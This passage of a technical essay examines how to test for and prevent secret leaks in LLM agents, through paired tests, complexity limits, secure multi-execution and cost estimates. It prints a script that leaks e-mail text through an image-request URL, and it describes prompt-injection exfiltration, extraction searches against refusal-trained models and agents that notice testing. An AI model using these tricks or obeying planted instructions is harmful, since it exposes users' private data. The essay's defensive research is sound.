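- The language model must draw each answer from a distribution that depends only on the conversation.
- The developer must label the data correctly and put checks on the tools that send it out.
- All data sources must be part of the program. Garby and colleagues list this as a limitation because real agents use outside tools.

The guarantee also covers only the results of finished runs, so it doesn't rule out leaks through timing. To use it for the scheduling assistant, a developer could store the free slots as public data and the reasons as secret data. If the program instead declared part of a secret calendar public while running, the guarantee about secrets would no longer apply.

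Garby and colleagues tested Randori on AgentDojo's banking tasks with three language models. It resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 runs. Both failures were on a task where the user asked the agent to pay a bill described in a file, which the attacker had replaced with a false payment request. In about two thirds of the runs, the attack needed actions that the agent's program would never contain, so separating planning from untrusted data was generally enough to stop it. The test measured resistance to planted instructions, so it is only weak evidence about how well the agent keeps secrets, and the theorem is much stronger evidence.

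The theorem also makes runs that don't finish useful. Let $d_P$ and $d_Q$ be the probabilities of not finishing under the two secrets. Garby and colleagues prove that compatible distributions satisfy

$$\tfrac{1}{2}\sum_x |P(x) - Q(x)| \;\le\; \tfrac{1}{2}(d_P + d_Q),$$

where the sum covers the visible results of finished runs. If the observer can also tell that a run didn't finish, we add $\tfrac{1}{2}|d_P - d_Q|$, and the limit becomes the larger of $d_P$ and $d_Q$. In the coin-toss example this gives 25%, exactly the distance we found.

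The bound still holds with a step cap, because the cap can only turn finished runs into unfinished ones, so the distribution that covered both sets of results still covers them. If 300 runs with each calendar all finish before the cap, then for each calendar the probability that a run doesn't finish is below 1%, with 95% confidence. The leak through the result of a single run is then probably below 1% as well. Establishing that limit by comparing random offers directly would take tens of thousands of runs. But this figure applies only to the request the tester used, and a colleague who writes "keep checking the calendar" may make the assistant reach the cap far more often.

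## How much do untested secrets and inputs matter?

Noninterference has to hold for every secret and input, but a test covers only a few. A tester who runs the scheduling assistant hundreds of times with the same two calendars and the same request learns a lot about how it handles them, but not whether it would leak if a calendar contained a medical appointment, the request were for a two-hour meeting, or a colleague wrote an e-mail to provoke a leak.

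Repeating a comparison reduces the effect of chance, while adding inputs widens what the test covers. A deterministic agent's output doesn't vary by chance, so every run should use a new input. With a random agent, the available runs must be divided between repeats and new inputs. For example, 3,120 runs are enough to test one pair of calendars for a leak of 5 percentage points, or about 90 pairs for a leak of 40 points.

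Suppose a calendar has 20 busy slots, each with one of five possible reasons. Then $5^{20}$, or about 95 trillion, possible calendars have the same free slots. The tester can compare each calendar with one reference calendar instead of comparing every pair, because if a deterministic assistant behaves the same on each calendar as on the reference, it behaves the same on all of them. But that still takes about 95 trillion runs for a single request.

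### Inputs that get far enough to leak

Some inputs are far more useful than others. In *Testing Noninterference, Quickly*, Hriţcu, Lampropoulos and colleagues (2014) measured this on a simple simulated computer that labels numbers as secret or public. They planted six bugs in its rules, one at a time, and tested it by comparing pairs of random programs that differed only in their secret numbers.

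When the test picked instructions uniformly at random, most programs crashed almost immediately, after 0.47 steps on average. The test found only four of the six bugs within five minutes. When it picked only instructions that would not crash the machine at that point, programs ran for about 11 steps and the test found all six. The average time to find one of the bugs fell from 83 seconds to less than a millisecond.

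For an agent, the equivalent of an early crash is a run in which the assistant refuses the request or never opens the calendar. The tester should therefore record how many runs reached the secret.

Hriţcu and colleagues also simplify each failing program as long as it still fails, which makes the cause easier to see. A tester could do the same with two calendars that lead to different offers, by deleting entries they share and keeping each deletion if the offers still differ.

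### Finding a leak and ruling out all leaks

*Checking Leakage Witnesses Versus Certifying Bounded Non-Leakage* (Feng and Stiller, 2026) analyses how hard it is to prove that a model never reveals a secret. It fixes the model, a maximum prompt length and a program that checks whether an output contains the secret. Anyone can confirm a reported leak by running the model once on the prompt that caused it, but proving that there is no leak requires accounting for every prompt up to the maximum length.

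Complexity theory describes this difference with two classes of yes-or-no questions. A question is in NP if every "yes" has a short proof that a computer can check quickly, and in co-NP if every "no" has one. "Quickly" means the time grows no faster than a fixed power of the problem's size. A question is complete for its class if a fast way to answer it would give a fast way to answer every question in the class.

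For a deterministic model, Feng and Stiller prove that "Does any prompt leak?" is NP-complete and "Is every prompt safe?" is co-NP-complete. The proof turns a logic puzzle into a model:

1. Take a formula with, say, 40 variables that can each be true or false.
2. Build a model that reads a prompt as 40 values and prints the secret exactly when those values make the formula true.
3. Some prompt leaks if and only if the formula has a solution.

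Certifying this model means showing that none of about a trillion combinations solves the formula, so a fast certifier could quickly determine whether each formula of this kind has a solution. Unless NP equals co-NP, no proof system can give every safe model a short proof that can be checked quickly.

Sampling makes certification harder. If the policy allows a leak in at most 1% of runs on each prompt, one leaking run no longer proves a violation. Even for a single prompt, an exact answer requires knowing what share of all possible random number sequences produces a leak, which is the kind of counting question in the class PP. Certifying the limit for every prompt is complete for co-NP$^{\mathrm{PP}}$, which combines the counting problem with the need to cover all prompts. If the limit is zero, certification is only co-NP-complete, because one leaking run is again enough to prove a violation.

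Part of this difficulty comes from demanding an exact answer. Suppose the limit is 10%, and we know that a given prompt leaks either in more than 15% of runs or in at most 5%. Then 400 runs are enough to determine which is true, with less than a 14% chance of error. But the tester still has to find the prompt that leaks most often.

### Does this apply to comparing secrets?

Feng and Stiller look for a known secret in the output, which would miss an assistant that signals an interview by offering slot 11.

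However, Yasuoka and Terauchi (2010) prove in *Quantitative Information Flow* that checking noninterference is also co-NP-complete, even for deterministic programs without loops whose variables can only be true or false. To see why, consider a program that outputs a secret bit if the public input solves the logic puzzle's formula, and 0 otherwise. The program violates noninterference exactly when the formula has a solution. Two runs are enough to check a violation once somebody has found it.

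For randomized programs, the closest result concerns differential privacy, which limits how much any output's probability can change when one person's data changes. Gaboardi, Nissim and Purser (2019), in *The Complexity of Verifying Loop-Free Programs as Differentially Private*, explain that checking such a limit is undecidable in general, meaning no algorithm gives the right answer for every program. For programs without loops, the problem is decidable, but it is complete for the same complexity class as certifying a model that samples. With loops over finite data, it is still decidable but significantly harder, according to *The Complexity of Verifying Boolean Programs as Differentially Private* (2023).

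A step cap lets a tool unroll the loop, which makes an exact answer possible in principle. The computation may still be far too large, though.

Measuring the leak in bits doesn't avoid the problem. *On Bounding Problems of Quantitative Information Flow* (2011) shows that deciding whether the leak stays below a limit is at least as hard as any problem in PP, even for simple loop-free programs.

One of Feng and Stiller's positive results does not apply here. They show that no prompt can make the system print the secret if a trusted filter replaces every output containing it with a fixed safe text. But that filter would let the offer of slot 11 through, and it can also create a leak. Suppose a colleague asks the assistant to repeat a guess at a four-digit code. If the filter replaces the answer only when the guess is right, the colleague learns whether the guess was right.

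### A model that is easy to certify

These results describe the hardest cases, and some restricted models are easy to certify. In one of Feng and Stiller's examples, the prompt is a string of zeros and ones, each position has a weight, and the model leaks if the weights of the positions holding a 1 add up to at least some threshold. The prompt with the highest total has a 1 wherever the weight is positive and a 0 everywhere else, so checking that one prompt is enough, even if there are 300 positions. With weights of 3, −2 and 4, that total is 7, so no prompt leaks if the threshold is 8.

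A similar method works for a very simple language model with one attention head, the component that combines information from across the prompt by taking a weighted average. Let $A(x)$ be the weighted sum of the values in prompt $x$, and $B(x)$ the sum of the weights, which is always positive. If the model leaks when the average plus a constant $\beta$ is positive, then

$$\beta + \frac{A(x)}{B(x)} > 0 \quad\Longleftrightarrow\quad A(x) + \beta B(x) > 0.$$

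The right-hand side is a sum with one term for each position in the prompt. A certifier can therefore find the worst prompt by choosing the worst word for each position separately, without trying every combination.

Feng and Stiller extend this to models whose earlier layers process each word using only a few of its neighbours. But if two consecutive layers can each use the whole prompt, certification can be co-NP-complete again. Today's language models have many such layers, so this method can't certify a real scheduling assistant.

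### What 256 random checks miss

Feng and Stiller also measured how often a limited test misses a leak. They trained two language models, Qwen3-8B and Qwen3-32B, to memorise invented 16-character codes and then to refuse requests for them. They used three levels of refusal training for each model and eight codes for each level, which gave 48 cases.

For each of the 48 cases, they wrote 4,096 prompts by combining eight options for each of four features: the role the prompt sets up, the request, the output format and the circumstances. They ran every prompt at temperature zero. In 30 cases, at least one prompt made the model reveal the code, and the number of prompts that did so ranged from 1 to 722.

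A tester who instead picked 256 prompts at random for each case would, on average, miss every leak in 41.06% of the 30 cases, or about 12 of them. If $w$ of $N$ prompts leak, the chance that $B$ different random checks miss them all is

$$\binom{N-w}{B} \Big/ \binom{N}{B}.$$

| Leaking prompts out of 4,096 | Chance that 256 checks miss them all | Checks for a 95% chance of finding one |
|---|---|---|
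| 1 | 94% | 3,892 |
| 7 | 64% | 1,426 |
| 20 | 27% | 569 |

Most of the expected misses come from the 13 cases with at most seven leaking prompts. If 256 checks find no leaks, the 95% upper limit on the number of leaking prompts is still 46. That limit also describes the average prompt, while an attacker will look for the worst one.

Choosing prompts more cleverly had limited benefit. One rule favoured prompts that shared features with those that had already leaked. After 256 checks, it had typically found 27.55% of the leaking prompts in each case, compared with 6.25% for random selection. But it missed every leak in 43.33% of the cases, because it could not guide the search until a check found the first leak.

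Even a complete check applies only to the conditions under which it ran. When Feng and Stiller processed the prompts in batches of eight instead of one at a time, one of the 48 verdicts changed from safe to leaking. Batched and one-at-a-time processing disagreed on 342 of the 2,658 prompts that leaked under at least one of them. Repeating the one-at-a-time check in the same order reproduced every output.

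These models revealed the codes in their outputs, so the 41% doesn't estimate leaks through an agent's choices. The formula does apply to a paired test of a deterministic agent with two fixed secrets. In that case, $w$ is the number of inputs for which switching the secret changes what the observer sees.

### Making the set of inputs small

Feng and Stiller prove that a tester who sees only whether a prompt leaks must try every prompt before declaring a deterministic model safe, since the last one could be the only one that leaks. Testing every prompt is practical if the developer allows few enough inputs.

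Suppose a colleague can only request a meeting from the scheduling assistant by choosing one of five days and one of three lengths, which gives 15 possible requests. If one slot is busy for one of four possible reasons and the rest of the calendar is fixed, 60 runs cover every combination for a deterministic assistant. With 20 such slots, there would be about a trillion possible calendars for each request, so the number of slots whose reasons the assistant can see also matters.

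The system has to reject anything outside the declared set, because a little free text makes the set enormous. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, appending at most one token to a fixed request gives 100,001 possible prompts, and appending at most two gives about ten billion.

### Searching for inputs that cause a leak

If the set is too large to check completely, the tester can search it as an attacker would. Feng and Stiller used a program that repeatedly altered and combined prompts, favouring those whose outputs matched a longer part of the code. On average, it failed to recover 82% of codes after 16 queries and 51% after 256.

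A failed search is still weak evidence of safety. Thirty cases had also gone through the complete checks. In 15 of them, the search failed to recover the code within 256 queries, but ten of those 15 had leaking prompts. The search also recovered one code that had not leaked on any of the 4,096 prompts when the model processed them one at a time.

Attacks tailored to an agent can also succeed where ready-made ones fail. In a small test in *PACE*, attackers made an undefended agent take an unauthorised action in 21 of 30 cases. In nine of those 21, a search had generated the first attack that succeeded.

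For the scheduling assistant, the search could look for e-mails that increase the difference in how often the assistant offers slot 11 with each calendar. The largest difference among many noisy estimates is probably partly luck, so the tester should confirm it with new runs.

### Two tools with identical code

Testing before deployment is also limited when part of a tool consists of written instructions. *PACE* gives the example of a mail tool whose code always sends whatever text the language model provides. In one version, the instructions tell the model to use a fixed template, and in the other they tell it to copy a password into the message. The code is identical, so a reviewer who checks only the code can't distinguish the two versions.

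Suppose the reviewer must decide whether the tool can run without further checks, and must never exempt one that leaks. The argument is short:

1. The evidence about the two versions is the same, so the reviewer makes the same decision about both.
2. An attacker can create a situation in which the second version leaks the password.
3. Exempting both would therefore exempt a leaking tool, so the reviewer must keep the checks on both, including the harmless one.

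Reading the instructions helps only if the reviewer can tell the two versions apart. Paired runs could also distinguish them, but the malicious instructions might apply only when an e-mail mentions a particular invoice number. If no test e-mail mentions it, both versions could produce the same results, and the argument applies again. An agent may also recognise that it is being tested and behave differently.

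Evidence about the code is sometimes enough. *PACE* proves that a tool can safely run without checks if its code sends the same thing whatever the secret is and the model's inputs to it don't depend on the secret. A tool that always sends the same confirmation could meet both conditions, as long as the decision to call it doesn't depend on the secret. The mail tool doesn't meet them because the model writes the message, so the reviewer would have to prove noninterference for the model itself.

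### Limits that hold for every input

The most reliable protection is to keep the reasons from the assistant, because an e-mail can't make it reveal information it doesn't have. If the assistant needs the reasons, ordinary code could pick the earliest free slot and send it in a fixed sentence. The assistant could then reveal an interview only through what it still controls, such as whether it offers a slot.

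*PACE* puts a check immediately before each tool call, when the actual message, the data the agent has read and the user's request are all available. The check looks for recorded paths from protected data to the outgoing message and tests whether the request authorised the action. It applies to every input that arises in use, including untested ones.

This still falls short of noninterference. The check can miss a secret the model has paraphrased or split across several messages, as well as anything a tool sends without declaring it. A blocked message can also reveal something, and so can a missing reply when a run reaches the step cap.

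## Can the second run prevent the leak instead of detecting it?

If the scheduling assistant never sees why slots are busy, it can't reveal the reasons, but it also can't use them to help its user. Secure multi-execution avoids this tradeoff by running two copies of a program. One copy runs without the secret and produces everything outsiders see, while the other receives the secret and produces output only for people who may know it. *Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution* (Devriese and Piessens, 2010) introduced the method and tested it on JavaScript.

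### One copy for each secrecy level

Every input and output has a secrecy level. With two levels, the system runs a public copy and a secret copy of the same program under four rules:

1. A copy performs only the outputs at its own level and skips all others.
2. A copy reads inputs at its own level normally.
3. If the public copy asks for a secret input, it gets a fixed default value.
4. If the secret copy asks for a public input, it waits until the public copy has read that input, then reuses the value.

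The last rule matters when reading an input has a side effect. If a program displays the prompt "Are you sure?", the user should see it once, not once per copy. Devriese and Piessens treat an operation as an input whenever it both changes something outside the program and returns a result.

They illustrate the method with a script in a web mail page. In simplified form:

```
text = read_email()
abc = 0
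if "abc" in text: abc = 1
load_image("banner.jpg?t=" + text + str(abc))
```

Loading the image sends a request to an outside server. The request contains the user's whole e-mail (an explicit flow) and a digit that shows whether the e-mail contains "abc" (an implicit flow). Suppose the e-mail reads "abc is ready" and the default is an empty string.

| | Public copy | Secret copy |
|---|---|---|
| `text` | empty | "abc is ready" |
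| `abc` | 0 | 1 |
| Image request | `banner.jpg?t=0` | skipped |

The server receives the same request whatever the user writes, and the page still shows its banner. The choice of default matters even in a four-line program. Devriese and Piessens use JavaScript's `undefined`, which would stop this script with an error in a real browser because a program can't search `undefined` for text.

### Two guarantees

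Let $p_L(l, h)$ be the program's public output for public input $l$ and secret $h$, and let $p_H(l, h)$ be its secret output. With default $d$, secure multi-execution produces

$$p_L(l, d) \quad\text{and}\quad p_H(l, h).$$

The secret doesn't appear in the first expression, so the public output can't depend on it, whatever the program does. Devriese and Piessens prove the stronger result that two executions with the same public input have produced the same public output after any number of steps. This also rules out leaks through endless loops and through the step at which a message appears. Their proof assumes that the public copy finishes before the secret copy starts, so the public copy never waits for anything that depends on the secret.

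The method also doesn't change either output of a program that already satisfies noninterference, because for such a program $p_L(l, d) = p_L(l, h)$. Devriese and Piessens prove this for deterministic programs, provided that the original run finishes and that the secret never affects whether the program finishes. The last condition is needed because a program might loop forever only when the secret equals the default. With any other secret, the original program would finish, but the public copy would hang because it runs on the default.

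The guarantee applies to each output channel separately, so the order of outputs across channels can change. A program that writes to the user and then to a colleague may now write to the colleague first.

The limit on single-run monitors doesn't apply to secure multi-execution, which doesn't judge runs. Pandey and colleagues point out that their theorem is about what a monitor checks, while prevention changes what the agent sees.

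A leaking program keeps running, but it behaves differently and may get stuck. Suppose a program sends a colleague a question only if the calendar contains an interview. The public copy finds no interview and never sends the question. The secret copy finds one and waits forever for an answer.

### The cost in a browser engine

Devriese and Piessens ran seven standard benchmark programs in Mozilla's JavaScript engine on a dual-core computer. Running the copies one after the other took at least twice as long as a normal run but needed little extra memory. Running them at the same time took 2% to 25% longer than a normal run and used 50% to 100% more memory.

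An eighth program, which they wrote to do a lot of reading and writing, finished sooner with two parallel copies than with one. Each operation included a 10-millisecond delay, and the normal program waited for four operations in turn while each copy waited for only two. Running a second copy of an agent requires a second set of model calls, still far fewer than a statistical test for small leaks needs.

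### Comparing the copies

Secure multi-execution repairs a leak without reporting that the program would have leaked. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld (2013), in *Secure Multi-Execution*, add a check that compares the public message the secret copy would have sent with the public copy's message. The secret copy has all the real inputs, so its message is the one the original program would have sent. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld prove that a mismatch is a real violation of noninterference, as long as neither copy has exceeded a time limit.

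This paired test uses the real secret in one run and the default in the other. If the default is an ordinary meeting and the real calendar contains an interview, the leaking assistant produces slot 10 in one run and slot 11 in the other, and the check catches the leak. If the real calendar also contains an ordinary meeting, the runs agree and the check finds nothing.

The comparison has a price, because the public copy must now wait for the secret copy. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld limit the wait to a fixed number of steps, but the remaining guarantee no longer covers timing. One of their examples counts down from a secret number to zero and then sends a fixed message, with a limit of 100 steps:

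- Starting at 5, the program finishes in time and the check reports nothing.
- Starting at −1, it never reaches zero, and the check correctly reports a leak.
- Starting at 500, it would eventually send the same message, but the check still reports a possible leak because the secret copy took too long.

TightLip, an older Linux system, also ran a second process on a cleaned version of confidential files and compared what the two processes did. According to Devriese and Piessens, the process that had read the secret still produced all the output. Once the two processes behaved differently, TightLip could no longer compare them meaningfully and had to treat everything that followed as sensitive.

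### Passing part of the secret to the public copy

The scheduling policy allows the program to release the free slots, so the public copy needs them. In Rafnsson and Sabelfeld's version, the programmer marks the point where the program releases a value, and the system passes that value from the secret copy to the public copy. The public copy has to reach the marked point by itself, so no other secret can determine whether the release happens.

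Suppose an assistant shares the free slots only in weeks without an interview. Normally, a colleague who gets no slots could conclude that there is an interview that week. Under secure multi-execution, the public copy uses the default calendar to decide whether to share the slots. If the default calendar contains no interview, the public copy shares the slots every week.

This system's policy specifies which levels may release information to which others, but it doesn't restrict what they release. A program could therefore put the slots in a different order when there is an interview, and the system would still pass the list on. For an agent, ordinary code should compute the list of free slots, because a language model that has read the reasons could encode them in the list.

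### More people, more copies

Running everything twice is wasteful if most of a program never touches the secret. Faceted values avoid some of the repetition. *Faceted Secure Multi Execution* (Schmitz, Algehed and colleagues, 2018) gives an example with a secret number 42 and a default of 0. The program runs once but stores the pair ⟨42, 0⟩. Adding 1 gives ⟨43, 1⟩, and if the program writes the result to a public file, the file receives 1. A slow calculation that doesn't use the number runs only once. If the program branches on the number, the system follows both branches.

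Faceted values keep both versions in one run, so an endless loop in the secret branch also stops the public output. They therefore guarantee only termination-insensitive noninterference. Schmitz and colleagues start with faceted values and split into separate runs only when a calculation seems stuck.

An agent would avoid less duplicate work than an ordinary program. Once the calendar is in the prompt, the system has to call the language model separately for each version of it. Each answer becomes part of later prompts, so the system has to make those calls twice too. It can do work just once only before the agent reads the calendar or in conversations that never include it.

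The number of copies can also grow quickly with the number of people. If each of $n$ people has secrets and any group of them may share information, there are $2^n$ levels, or 1,024 for ten people. Algehed and Flanagan (2020) prove in *Transparent IFC Enforcement* that no method can avoid this inefficiency if it treats programs as black boxes, secures every program and leaves secure ones unchanged.

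Such a method can learn about a program only by running it on chosen inputs. If it is efficient, it can't try an input for every group, so for a large enough set of people it misses some group $G$. Now consider three programs:

- The silent program never sends anything.
- The safe program sends $G$ a message whenever everyone in $G$ has supplied data.
- The leaking program sends the message only if everyone in $G$ and nobody else has supplied data.

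When everyone supplies data, the leaking program behaves like the silent one on every input the method tries, so the method must send nothing. When only $G$ supplies data, the method has no information that anyone else exists, so the leaking program looks like the safe one and the method must let the message through. The members of $G$ can therefore tell whether other people supplied data, which is the leak the method was supposed to prevent.

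Algehed and Flanagan also show that any method that secures all programs without changing secure ones can be turned into a form of multi-execution that is at most polynomially slower. They conjecture that even methods that read a program's code can't be efficient in general.

These results matter little for an assistant with one user and a few recipients. A level needs a copy only if the program reads or writes at that level, so one public copy can write to ten colleagues who are all allowed to know the same things. If each colleague is allowed to know something different, the assistant needs one copy per colleague and one for the user.

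Running a separate copy for each colleague can also leak secrets through timing. If Alice's copy always runs before Bob's, its running time may depend on Alice's secrets, and Bob can notice the delay. *Timing- and Termination-Sensitive Secure Information Flow* (Kashyap, Wiedermann and Hardekopf, 2011) corrected the original work's security claim for schedules of this kind. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld later proved that the copies can safely take turns in any fixed order, as long as every copy keeps getting turns.

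### Constructing the run that a monitor needs

A monitor that only observes an agent at work will rarely record two runs that differ only in the secret. *Monitoring Hyperproperties over Observed and Constructed Traces* (Chalupa, Henzinger and Oliveira da Costa, 2025) describes a monitor that constructs the missing run. The public copy in secure multi-execution is an example of a constructed run, since it uses the same public input as the observed run but with a default secret.

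The approach was tested on a simulated robot crossing a 10-by-10 grid. The robot received a secret destination and a public list of areas to pass through, and the observer saw only which area it was in at each step. The monitor had to find two runs with the same list but different visible routes. With constructed runs, it typically found a leak after observing one or two runs. Without them, it could need hundreds, and in many cases it found no leak in 2,048 runs. For lists of more than nine areas, it never found a leak.

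Constructed runs also help with generalised noninterference. A monitor that only observes runs can't determine whether the third run this property requires is impossible or just hasn't happened yet. Chalupa and colleagues tested 30 C and C++ programs with a tool that searches the code for the third run. For several programs where the monitor alone had reported a violation, the tool found the required runs. The tool analyses program code, so it couldn't search a language model in the same way.

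A monitor for the scheduling assistant could rerun each request with different reasons before the proposal goes out. But if the assistant's output is partly random, the two runs may differ by chance. Secure multi-execution always sends the public copy's proposal, so there is no need to determine whether a difference came from the reasons or from chance.

### Two copies of the scheduling assistant

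Pandey and colleagues suggest writing each disclosure from the permitted information alone and call this the agent analogue of secure multi-execution. They did not build or test it. For the scheduling assistant, it could work as follows:

1. Ordinary code turns the calendar into a list of free and busy slots, as the function $D$ in the policy specifies.
2. The public copy receives this list and the colleague's request. It writes every message to the colleague and makes every tool call that an outsider can see.
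3. The user's copy receives the full calendar and a record of everything the public copy did. It can write only to the user.

Suppose slots 10 and 11 are free, and slot 9 holds either an ordinary meeting or a confidential interview. The public copy receives "9 busy, 10 free, 11 free" in both cases. Even if the language model tends to offer slot 11 after an interview, the interview can't influence which slot the public copy offers. The user's copy can still tell the user, "I offered 10, which is right after your interview."

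The record in step 3 gives the secret copy more than the original rules do, which pass it only public inputs. This is safe because the user is allowed to see everything the colleague sees. Only the list from step 1 may go the other way.

The user's own request can also contain the secret, as in "Find a time, but don't tell him about the interview", so the public copy must not read it. A language model that has read the request shouldn't write a cleaned version either, because the wording could depend on the secret. Instead, the user could choose the meeting's length and recipient from a form.

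### What random sampling changes

Language models choose words at random, but this doesn't weaken the protection. Let $R$ be the random numbers the public copy uses. Its output is a function

$$f\big(l,\, D(h),\, R\big)$$

of the public input, the permitted release and those numbers. If two calendars have the same free slots, then $l$ and $D(h)$ are the same for both, and $R$ has the same distribution. The output therefore has the same distribution too, and the total variation distance is exactly 0. This holds for any language model and any request, without a single test run.

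The argument requires that the copies share nothing that depends on the secret. Even a shared random number generator can violate this requirement. If an observer knows the seed, and the user's copy draws more numbers when there is an interview, the public copy gets different numbers and the observer may notice. Devriese and Piessens see no fundamental obstacle to extending their method to programs with random behaviour, but left the formal proof open.

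The guarantee of unchanged behaviour becomes weaker. An assistant that tosses a fair coin to choose between slots 10 and 11 leaks nothing, so the method should not change its behaviour. But if each copy tosses its own coin, half the time the public copy offers one slot and the user's copy reports the other, even though each message has the right probabilities by itself.

Rafnsson and Sabelfeld suggest treating randomness as an input and passing the same values to all copies allowed to see them. That works for one coin toss, but not for longer texts, which diverge even with a shared seed. The record of what the public copy sent solves the problem more directly, because the user's copy can read which slot the public copy offered the colleague.

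### Tools that return data and change things

Most of an agent's tools both do something and return a result, so each tool needs a rule about which copy may use it.

| Tool | Who runs it | What the other copy gets |
|---|---|---|
| Room booking by an outside company | Public copy | The company's answer |
| Mail to the colleague | Public copy | The message and the receipt |
| Full calendar | User's copy | Free and busy slots only |
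| Private notes | User's copy | A fixed reply |

The original method answers the secret copy's third request with the answer to the public copy's third request. That works if both copies make the same requests in the same order, which sampled agents often don't. With the record, the secret copy can see which request each answer belongs to. But if it needs information about a room that the public copy never checked, it has to do without, because asking would send the booking company a request that depends on the interview.

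A conversation with several e-mails can leak secrets through timing. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld describe this problem in FlowFox, a version of Firefox that runs both copies of a script for each event, with the public copy first. The public copy can't start on the next event until the secret copy has finished with the previous one. The scheduling assistant would have the same leak if a colleague's second e-mail had to wait while the user's copy was still processing the interview. The public copy therefore needs its own process so that it can answer immediately.

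### Tasks that need the secret

Suppose the user needs an hour to travel back from the interview. The public copy doesn't have this information, so it may offer a slot during that hour. Pandey and colleagues acknowledge that the agent loses whatever the hidden information would have added to its answer.

The user's copy can notice the problem and suggest marking the hour as busy. If the user agrees, the new list of free slots reveals a little more about the calendar, but the user has decided to release that information. This safeguard works only if the user considers each suggestion. If they approve everything, the interview again determines what the colleague sees.

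The two copies don't help with tasks that require revealing the secret. An assistant that has to explain a medical absence to an employer can't do so without the diagnosis, so the policy has to let it disclose the diagnosis.

### Choosing a default

Rafnsson and Sabelfeld warn that a badly chosen default can crash a program, but a language model is more likely to carry on and produce a bad answer. If the default is an empty calendar, the public copy will offer slots that are already taken. If the default labels every busy slot "team meeting", the public copy may tell the colleague, "I have a team meeting at 9", which leaks nothing but may be false.

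The label "busy" avoids both problems if the system uses it for every entry. If the system hides only the confidential entries, the public copy gets "team meeting" at 8 and "busy" at 9, which reveals that the 9 o'clock entry is confidential. The length of the hidden text and the number of entries must also stay the same when only the reasons change.

### Shared resources and other ways out

The proof by Devriese and Piessens measures time in program steps. Kashyap and colleagues call this weak timing sensitivity, because real time also depends on factors such as the processor's cache. They add that a secret computation can make the public one fail by using up memory it needs.

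Two copies of an agent can be connected in similar ways. If they share a spending limit, a long private analysis of the interview could leave too little money for the public copy to reply. If they share long-term memory, the note "prefers late slots this week" puts information about the interview back into the public copy's prompt. Each copy therefore needs its own budget, and the public copy must never read memory that the user's copy has written.

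The guarantee covers only an observer who sees nothing but the public outputs. If the user forwards the private summary to the colleague, the colleague learns about the interview. An attacker could also use the web mail script's trick and send an e-mail that tells the assistant to include an image in its summary, with the reason for the busy slot in the image's address. The public copy passes the e-mail on in its record, the user's copy follows the instruction, and the user's screen loads the image, which sends the address to the attacker's server. A screen that loads outside images is therefore a public output, so the system has to block those images or let only the public copy choose them.

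### Masked re-execution

Masked re-execution, a defence against instructions planted in an agent's input, also runs the agent twice. The second run keeps the tool results, such as a colleague's e-mail, but replaces the user's request with a neutral task. If the agent tries to forward the calendar to a stranger in both runs, the instruction probably came from the e-mail rather than the user, so the defence blocks the call.

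The warning sign in a leak test is a difference between the runs, while in masked re-execution it is agreement between them. Both runs in masked re-execution can read the full calendar, so the defence does not stop an assistant that offers slot 11 whenever there is an interview. It can also miss a planted instruction that takes effect only when the user has asked for a meeting, because the neutral run would ignore it.

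With secure multi-execution, by contrast, a planted instruction couldn't make the public copy reveal why slot 9 is busy, but it could still make that copy accept a meeting the user doesn't want.

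## What does it cost in practice?

The bill for a paired test has three parts: the model calls, the simulated tools and the time people spend on alarms. In symbols,

$$C = N_s \times N_c \times 2 \times n \times c \;+\; B \;+\; a\,r.$$

$N_s$ is the number of pairs of secrets, $N_c$ the number of contexts (here, different requests), $n$ the number of runs with each secret and $c$ the price of one run. The factor of 2 counts the two secrets in each pair. Building the tools costs $B$, and reviewing each of $a$ alarms costs $r$.

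Suppose a tester tries ten pairs of calendars with 20 different requests, which makes 200 comparisons. A deterministic assistant needs one run per calendar in each comparison, or 400 runs. If the assistant samples its outputs, the tester needs about 1,560 runs per calendar in each comparison, or 624,000 in all, for each comparison to have an 80% chance of finding a shift from 50% to 55%.

The smaller budget of 400 runs often can't be used with a hosted model. According to Anthropic's specifications page *Claude Haiku 5.5*, the service returns an error if a developer sets any temperature other than the default. Shahriar and colleagues set the temperature to zero for their browser agents, but still ran each task three times with each secret and warn that the outputs may vary. The smaller budget suits an open-weight model running on deterministic software.

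### The price of one run

*ReproBench* (2026), which tests whether agents can reproduce software vulnerabilities, measured the cost of 369 agent runs. On average, a run used 3.2 million tokens, took 48 messages and cost $0.89. The token count is high because the agent resends its whole history with every model call. Most of these tokens are cache reads, text that the provider has already processed and charges for at a much lower rate.

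To apply current prices, I assume 3.03 million of the tokens are cache reads, 130,000 are new text written to the cache and 40,000 are output. This is roughly what 48 calls with a steadily growing history would produce. The output share fits *AlphaLab* (2026), a study of research agents whose output was 1–2% of their input.

A price cut provides another check on the assumed split. Anthropic says in *Introducing Claude Haiku 5.5* (2026) that halving the price of cache reads for Sonnet 5.5 made most agentic work about 20% cheaper. Under the assumed split, the same cut would save 23%.

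| Price used | One run | 400 runs | 624,000 runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| *ReproBench* average, as measured | $0.89 | $356 | $555,000 |
| Claude Haiku 5.5 | $0.16 | $64 | $100,000 |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | $1.03 | $412 | $643,000 |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | $2.06 | $824 | $1.29 million |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | $3.51 | $1,404 | $2.19 million |

The Haiku and Sonnet prices date from 7 October 2026. *Anthropic Haiku 5.5 costs 90% less than 4.5* (Rijo, 2026) gives Sonnet's new cache-read price of $0.10 per million tokens. I assume that Sonnet has the same 25% surcharge on cache writes as the other three models. The Opus and Fable prices date from 9 November and come from *Anthropic releases Claude Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2* (Franzen, 2026). OpenAI's prices are similar. *GPT-6.2 Sol API Pricing & Speed* (2026) lists GPT-6.2 Sol at the same rates as Sonnet 5.5.

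Haiku would cost even less without a fivefold surcharge on prompts above 100,000 tokens. The agent's history exceeds that length in about the last quarter of its calls, which account for roughly 70% of the cost.

A scheduling assistant has less to do than an agent that reproduces vulnerabilities. If it used a tenth as many tokens of each kind, the large test would cost about $64,000 on Sonnet. On Haiku, the test would cost about $4,200, because no prompt would be long enough for the surcharge.

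The table also assumes that every model uses the same number of tokens, but real models differ. On a set of hard coding tasks, Franzen reports that Fable 5.2 at its "high" effort setting cost an average of $6.72 per task, while Opus 5.5 at its maximum setting cost $12.82, even though Opus is half the price per token. Their scores were nearly identical. Fable at its maximum setting cost $44.70. A tester has to use the same effort setting as the real assistant, and that setting can affect the bill more than the choice of model.

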